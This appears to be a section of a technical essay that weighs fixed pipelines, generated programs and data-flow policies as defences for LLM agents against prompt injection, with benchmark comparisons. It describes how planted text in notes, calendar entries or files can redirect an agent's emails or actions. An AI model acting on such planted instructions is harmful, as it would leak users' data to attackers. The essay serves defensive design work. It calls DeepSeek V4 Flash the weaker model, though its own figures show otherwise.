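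A model that chooses from a menu of fixed pipelines can handle more requests than a single pipeline can. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) calls this the action-selector pattern. In its example, a customer-service chatbot can fetch a link to the customer's last order or refer the customer to the settings for passwords or payment. The results never go back to the model, so text in them can't influence its choice. The paper describes such agents as immune to prompt injection, which is true of the choice of action. But if one of the actions is the pipeline for Bob, `extract` still reads the notes, and a false address in them still reaches `send_email`.

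When the model can choose its own sequence of tool calls, the user isn't limited to a fixed menu of tool sequences. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of an assistant asked to send today's schedule to the user's boss. It plans to read the calendar and then send an email to the boss's address. Text planted in a calendar entry can change the body of that email but can't redirect it, because the user supplied the address. Bob's address comes from the notes, so an attacker can redirect the email to him by planting text there. What an injection can change therefore depends as much on where each value comes from as on the design.

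A straight sequence can't do much with the results. Suppose that Bob wants the latest version of the document and the search tool returns all of them:

```python
versions = find_versions(title)
latest = versions[0]
for v in versions:
    if v.date > latest.date:
        latest = v
send_email(to=address, subject="The document you asked for",
           attachment=latest)
```

One user may want the latest version, another the last version before Friday, and another the shortest. The developer could supply a separate tool for each comparison, but the small language can express all of them. Its loops, branches and pure operators make programs more useful without giving them new effects on the outside world, because the proof that programs have no effects beyond the listed tools already covers these features.

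A program can call the model again when its next step can't be written in advance. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a bibliography agent fetches one search result and passes it to a new model call. The model can then check whether the search terms were good before writing the code that fills the bibliography. LACUNA can split up a report in the same way, with one model call for each topic and another to combine the findings.

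The middle column of the table also shows what a hostile model controls. It can run the wrong pipeline or fill in the wrong name if it is given a menu, and it can write whatever the policy permits under any of the last three designs.

### Why rules have to cover sequences

Take six tools: `read_notes`, `extract`, `find_file`, `send_email`, one that looks up a contact and one that adds a calendar entry. If a plan may have up to five steps and may use a tool more than once, the number of possible sequences is:

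6 + 6² + 6³ + 6⁴ + 6⁵ = 9,330

At a minute per sequence, a developer would need almost four working weeks to review them all, and the count ignores arguments, branches and loops. Most of these sequences are useless, and 20 pipelines may well cover nearly everything a company's staff ask for. The count is therefore a weak argument against pipelines, but it is a better argument that a policy for a language can't be a list of approved programs.

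In 1,714 of the 9,330 sequences, the agent reads the notes at some point before it sends an email. (Among the sequences with n steps, the agent never reads the notes in 5ⁿ, and it reads them but sends no email afterwards in n × 5ⁿ⁻¹.) One rule that keeps text from the notes away from outside addresses covers all these sequences and every longer program.

A guard inside `send_email` can't always apply such a rule by itself, because it receives the text of the message but no record of whether that text came from the notes. Either a checker has to follow the data through the program, or the interpreter has to label the data with its source. The objection leaves this out by treating guarded tools as separate from the code that connects them.

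### What a whole program adds to safety

A verifier can check more when the model writes the whole program in advance than when an agent makes one call at a time. When a call-by-call agent fetches the user's mail, its software can't tell whether the next call will send that mail to a stranger. Meijer points out that a monitor that stops the outgoing message acts only after the agent has read and processed the private emails. A verifier that has the whole plan can reject it before the agent fetches anything.

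Refusing the whole program also avoids half-finished work. An agent that makes one call at a time might withdraw money from one account before its next call fails because the tool doesn't exist. In LACUNA's example, the whole program was refused and the balance stayed at 100.

The program can also use data that the model that wrote it never reads. Agents that make single tool calls can do this too. FIDES, for example, stores untrusted results in variables. But a model that can't see the documents' dates can't compare them, so such an agent needs a tool or a second model to do it. A generated program can compare the dates itself.

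A fixed pipeline has all of these advantages too. The developer knows every step before the first run, can reject a bad plan during review, and can keep the data away from any planning model. Compared with a fixed pipeline, generated code adds no safety and some risk. A reviewer approves the specific steps in a pipeline, but a policy allows any program that complies with it, including one that deletes every text file when only two needed to be deleted.

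Generated code is safer than letting a model choose each call after reading untrusted text, and it handles a wider range of requests than a fixed pipeline does. Neither comparison shows that it is the safest way to do a task that a developer foresaw.

### Code against ordinary tool calls

Meijer expected structured plans to improve an agent's answers compared with direct tool calls, but wrote that nobody had formally measured the effect. The TACIT and LACUNA papers have since compared their systems with ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent helps simulated customers while following a company's rules. The table gives the percentage of tasks solved with ordinary tool calls, then with generated Scala code.

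| System | Model | Airline | Retail | Telecom | Telecom workflow | Overall |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 → 45.2 | 53.3 → 57.0 | – | – | – |
| TACIT | MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 → 61.0 | 75.1 → 77.5 | – | – | – |
| TACIT | DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 → 58.6 | 74.6 → 75.5 | – | – | – |
| LACUNA | DeepSeek V4 Flash | 75.5 → 70.0 | 80.9 → 58.8 | 100.0 → 88.6 | 95.4 → 83.3 | 90.0 → 76.0 |
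| LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 56.0 → 38.0 | 52.6 → 43.9 | 15.8 → 14.9 | 21.1 → 24.6 | 33.2 → 29.1 |

TACIT did better than ordinary tool calls in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues ran each task ten times and averaged the results. They attribute the gain to the typed interface, which describes exactly what each tool returns, and to the compiler's error messages. If they are right, part of the gain came from better tool descriptions, which an ordinary tool-calling agent could also receive.

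Odersky and colleagues also tested TACIT on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 software problems from GitHub for the agent to fix. MiniMax M2.5 solved 43.3% with ordinary tools and 41.7% with TACIT. The difference of five problems could easily be chance. They suggest that coding depends more on working in a shell, which is awkward to express through TACIT's library.

LACUNA's results are worse. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, while the ordinary agent solved 90.0%. LACUNA solved about 55 fewer tasks and failed more than twice as often, so Zhao and colleagues are wrong to describe its result as "on par" with the ordinary agent's. If we treat the two results as independent samples, the 95% confidence interval for the difference runs from about 9 to 19 points, which makes chance a poor explanation.

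The phrase fits the weaker model better. With that model, LACUNA scored 29.1% against 33.2%, a gap of about 16 tasks, and the same calculation gives an interval from 2 points in LACUNA's favour to 11 points against it. Even with the weaker model, LACUNA was 18 points behind on the airline tasks.

Zhao and colleagues write that the gap for the weaker model, DeepSeek V4 Flash, is "the model's, not the primitive's", where the primitive is LACUNA's way of asking for code. That can't be the whole explanation, because the same model solved 90% of the tasks when it used the same domain tools through ordinary calls. It evidently knew how to help most of these customers but lost some of that ability when it had to act through LACUNA.

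### Rejected programs and other explanations

Few of TACIT's programs on τ²-bench failed to compile and needed a retry, which suggests that compile errors weren't the main cause. The highest retry rate was 7.93%, for DeepSeek V3.2 on the airline tasks, and compiling took less than a second. Some of the errors were trivial, such as leaving a dollar sign unescaped in Scala text, where it has a special meaning.

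With LACUNA, the compiler rejected 22.4% of the programs that DeepSeek V4 Flash wrote for retail tasks, or about seven per task. Retail tasks are long conversations, with 26.7 tool calls on average, and a program has to combine the company's rules with results from earlier turns. LACUNA's largest drop in performance with this model was also on retail tasks.

But rejections don't explain the pattern with Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite. On retail tasks, the compiler rejected only 3.2% of its programs, yet the model's success rate was 8.7 percentage points lower than with ordinary tool calls. This suggests that programs which passed the check often did the wrong thing. On telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of programs, but the success rate was only 0.9 points lower because the model solved few of these tasks either way.

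The way LACUNA handles conversations may be another cause. TACIT keeps the usual loop, in which the model receives the conversation and submits code through a tool call. LACUNA turns each customer message into a new request for code and keeps earlier questions, replies and results in a programming session, with no separate memory for the conversation. Zhao and colleagues concede that a conventional loop may manage a long history more efficiently. They also ran the models with reasoning disabled, which may hurt a model more when it has to write a whole program than when it chooses one call.

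Nobody has separated these causes by running TACIT and LACUNA with the same models and settings. The results so far suggest that writing typed code doesn't have to reduce success, since TACIT showed no clear loss, but that a particular design can reduce it substantially.

Zhao and colleagues also claim that type-checking did not reduce accuracy on BrowseComp-Plus, the benchmark of research questions. DeepSeek V4 Flash passed the check with little extra work, averaging 0.7 retries per question and needing none on two-thirds of questions. However, the experiment varied only the model and included no agent without the check, so it can't show that accuracy was unaffected.

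ELBA needed few retries too. Across 2,688 runs on AgentDojo, it averaged 0.13 retries per run and spent 3.4% of its time on them. Seven runs failed because the model couldn't write a valid program within the limit. ELBA used stronger models than LACUNA and different tasks, so these figures don't show whether Haskell is easier for models to write than Scala.

### The price of a policy

On τ²-bench, the code mostly had to satisfy the compiler. AgentDojo also tests what happens when a policy forbids some ways of doing a task. Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's completion rates there comparable to the published figures for CaMeL, but individual results differ widely in both directions. TACIT completed 52.86% of office tasks with o4-mini, compared with CaMeL's 81.4%, and 64.29% of travel tasks with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with CaMeL's 1.4%. CaMeL completed 74.3% of the travel tasks with o4-mini,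 so its low score with Gemini was probably due to a problem between that model and CaMeL's setup, not a general limit of planning first.

Zhou and colleagues ran both ELBA and CaMeL themselves, with the same models, on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. The table shows how many tasks each system completed without an attack.

| Model | ELBA, no policy | CaMeL, no policy | ELBA, with policy | CaMeL, with policy |
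|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 15 | 10 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 16 | 9 | 6 |
| GPT 5.4 | 16 | 17 | 10 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 13 | 8 | 4 |
| Total of 84 | 64 | 61 | 37 | 20 |

Even without a policy, CaMeL's planner writes its program before reading any data, while ELBA can read data and then ask for more code. That ability made little difference here, with 64 tasks completed against 61, and for each model the confidence interval for the difference includes zero. With direct injections in the data and no policy, ELBA completed 343 of 420 tasks and CaMeL completed 285.

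Turning on the policies reduced the number of completed tasks far more. ELBA lost 27 of its 64 completed tasks and CaMeL lost 41 of its 61. Zhou and colleagues attribute ELBA's advantage to its ability to write new programs in response to data, which also made it about three times as slow. But the two systems enforced different policies. ELBA lowered a model's privileges after the model read untrusted data, while CaMeL used its own rules. The roughly twofold difference in completed tasks therefore reflects the policies as well as the designs. Zhou and colleagues suggest standardising policies in future work.

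The policy also reduced the number of tasks ELBA completed in the worst-case test, where subagents obeyed the attacker. Depending on the model, ELBA completed between 294 and 351 of 735 tasks with the policy on, compared with between 494 and 558 without it. Each model completed between 33% and 44% fewer tasks with the policy on. If a company deployed such an agent with the policy on and had nobody to approve refused actions, more than half of these tasks would fail.

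A policy doesn't always reduce task completion this much. In TACIT's test with secret files, Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2% of tasks when the secrets were sealed and 83.3% when they weren't. MiniMax M2.5 completed 90.0% with the seal and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues think the result for Sonnet may be an artefact, because without the seal Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection. The agent could do these tasks without reading the secrets, whereas many Slack tasks need an action that depends on untrusted text.

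### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* calls a task data-independent if the agent can choose its steps without reading untrusted text. Sending Bob his document is data-independent because the model can determine that it needs an address and a title before reading either. "Do whatever the meeting notes ask me to do" is data-dependent because the steps depend on the requests in the notes, which might be to send a file, book a room or cancel a contract.

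Planning first doesn't necessarily reduce performance on data-independent tasks. The paper's agent, Prudentia, adds policy-aware planning to FIDES. In tests on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, it had to comment on a post or upvote it while the page contained other text meant to redirect it. Prudentia never needed to read the untrusted text or ask for approval, and it completed at least as many tasks as an unprotected agent with each of four models. With o3-mini on Reddit, Prudentia completed 58.3% of tasks, while the unprotected agent completed 25.0% because the planted instructions confused it.

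For data-dependent tasks, a program written in advance has to anticipate what the data might require. It could sort each request in the notes into "send a file", "book a room" or "other" and have a branch for each. An injection could then trigger only the branches the model had written, and the agent would leave "other" requests to the user. CaMeL is subject to this limit. The CaMeL paper reports that defences that enforce rules on data have reduced task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%.

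Calling the model again removes the need to foresee every case, but the policy still applies. Once the model has read the notes, its new program is untrusted, and a strict policy will stop that program from sending mail or cancelling anything, so the agent may need help to carry out what it decides to do.

If an email from a colleague lists ten tasks, the user can help by approving ten separate actions or by reading the email once and declaring it trustworthy. Prudentia can prompt the user for either. Declaring the email trustworthy saves time, but it means trusting every instruction in it, so the user has to read it more carefully than they would a single proposed action.

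The option to ask for approval also changes how to read the completion rates. Many earlier evaluations compare a protected agent that may never ask with an unprotected one that acts as if a person had approved everything. When the paper allowed no approvals for either kind of agent, an ordinary agent with o3-mini completed only 24.3% of AgentDojo's tasks, because it had to ask before every important action. FIDES completed 50.1% and Prudentia 59.1%.

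With o4-mini and unlimited approvals, Prudentia needed about 19 approvals per run of the benchmark, compared with 37 for FIDES, because its model had access to the policy and could look for a plan that complied. It completed slightly fewer tasks, 73.2% against 75.7%. If a rule blocks one way of doing a task, the model can look for another, while a fixed pipeline stops until a developer changes it.

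### When to prefer a fixed pipeline

None of these experiments included a fixed pipeline. Their baselines were agents that choose each tool call themselves or other systems that generate programs. The experiments show whether a model works better by writing code than by making tool calls, but not how many users a good set of pipelines would have served, or how much more reliably.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose design patterns for ten applications, which give a rough idea of where generated programs are useful. They suggest such programs for only two of the ten, an email and calendar assistant and a booking assistant. For a customer-service chatbot, they suggest a fixed set of actions. These are proposals, not measurements, but some of the researchers also helped design CaMeL.

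A fixed pipeline is the better choice when the same few tasks, such as paying approved invoices, come up repeatedly and a mistake would be expensive. The developer can test every step, nobody has to trust a checker for generated programs, and the agent doesn't have to plan or retry. The pipeline may still use a model where the task needs one. In another example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, a separate model reads each file and answers only whether it contains an invoice. The agent then emails the matching files to the accounts department. A malicious file can cause the model to include it wrongly, but it can't make the agent send a different file or use a different address.

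Generated programs are worth the added complexity when requests vary too much for a fixed menu and users would otherwise do the work by hand or give an agent free use of its tools. They can also require less model use than such an agent. In Zhou and colleagues' bibliography test, an ordinary agent made about four times as many model calls as ELBA and took in about 65 times as much text. That agent searched the web while ELBA queried DBLP, so the difference in text partly reflects the length of web pages. But ELBA's programs could also sort and filter entries without passing each one through a model.

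A developer can choose a different design for each task. Zhao and colleagues show three versions of a function that reviews a change to a program. The first has the model do the whole review. The second uses ordinary code to pick out the risky files and has the model review only those. The third contains no model call. All three have the same type, so a developer can replace one with another without changing the code that uses them.

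A practical way to start may be to have the agent generate a program, under the policy, for any request that users keep making and the menu doesn't cover. Once similar programs have come up often enough, a developer can review one, turn the parts that vary into parameters, and add it to the menu. For later requests of that kind, the model only has to choose the pipeline and fill in the parameters.
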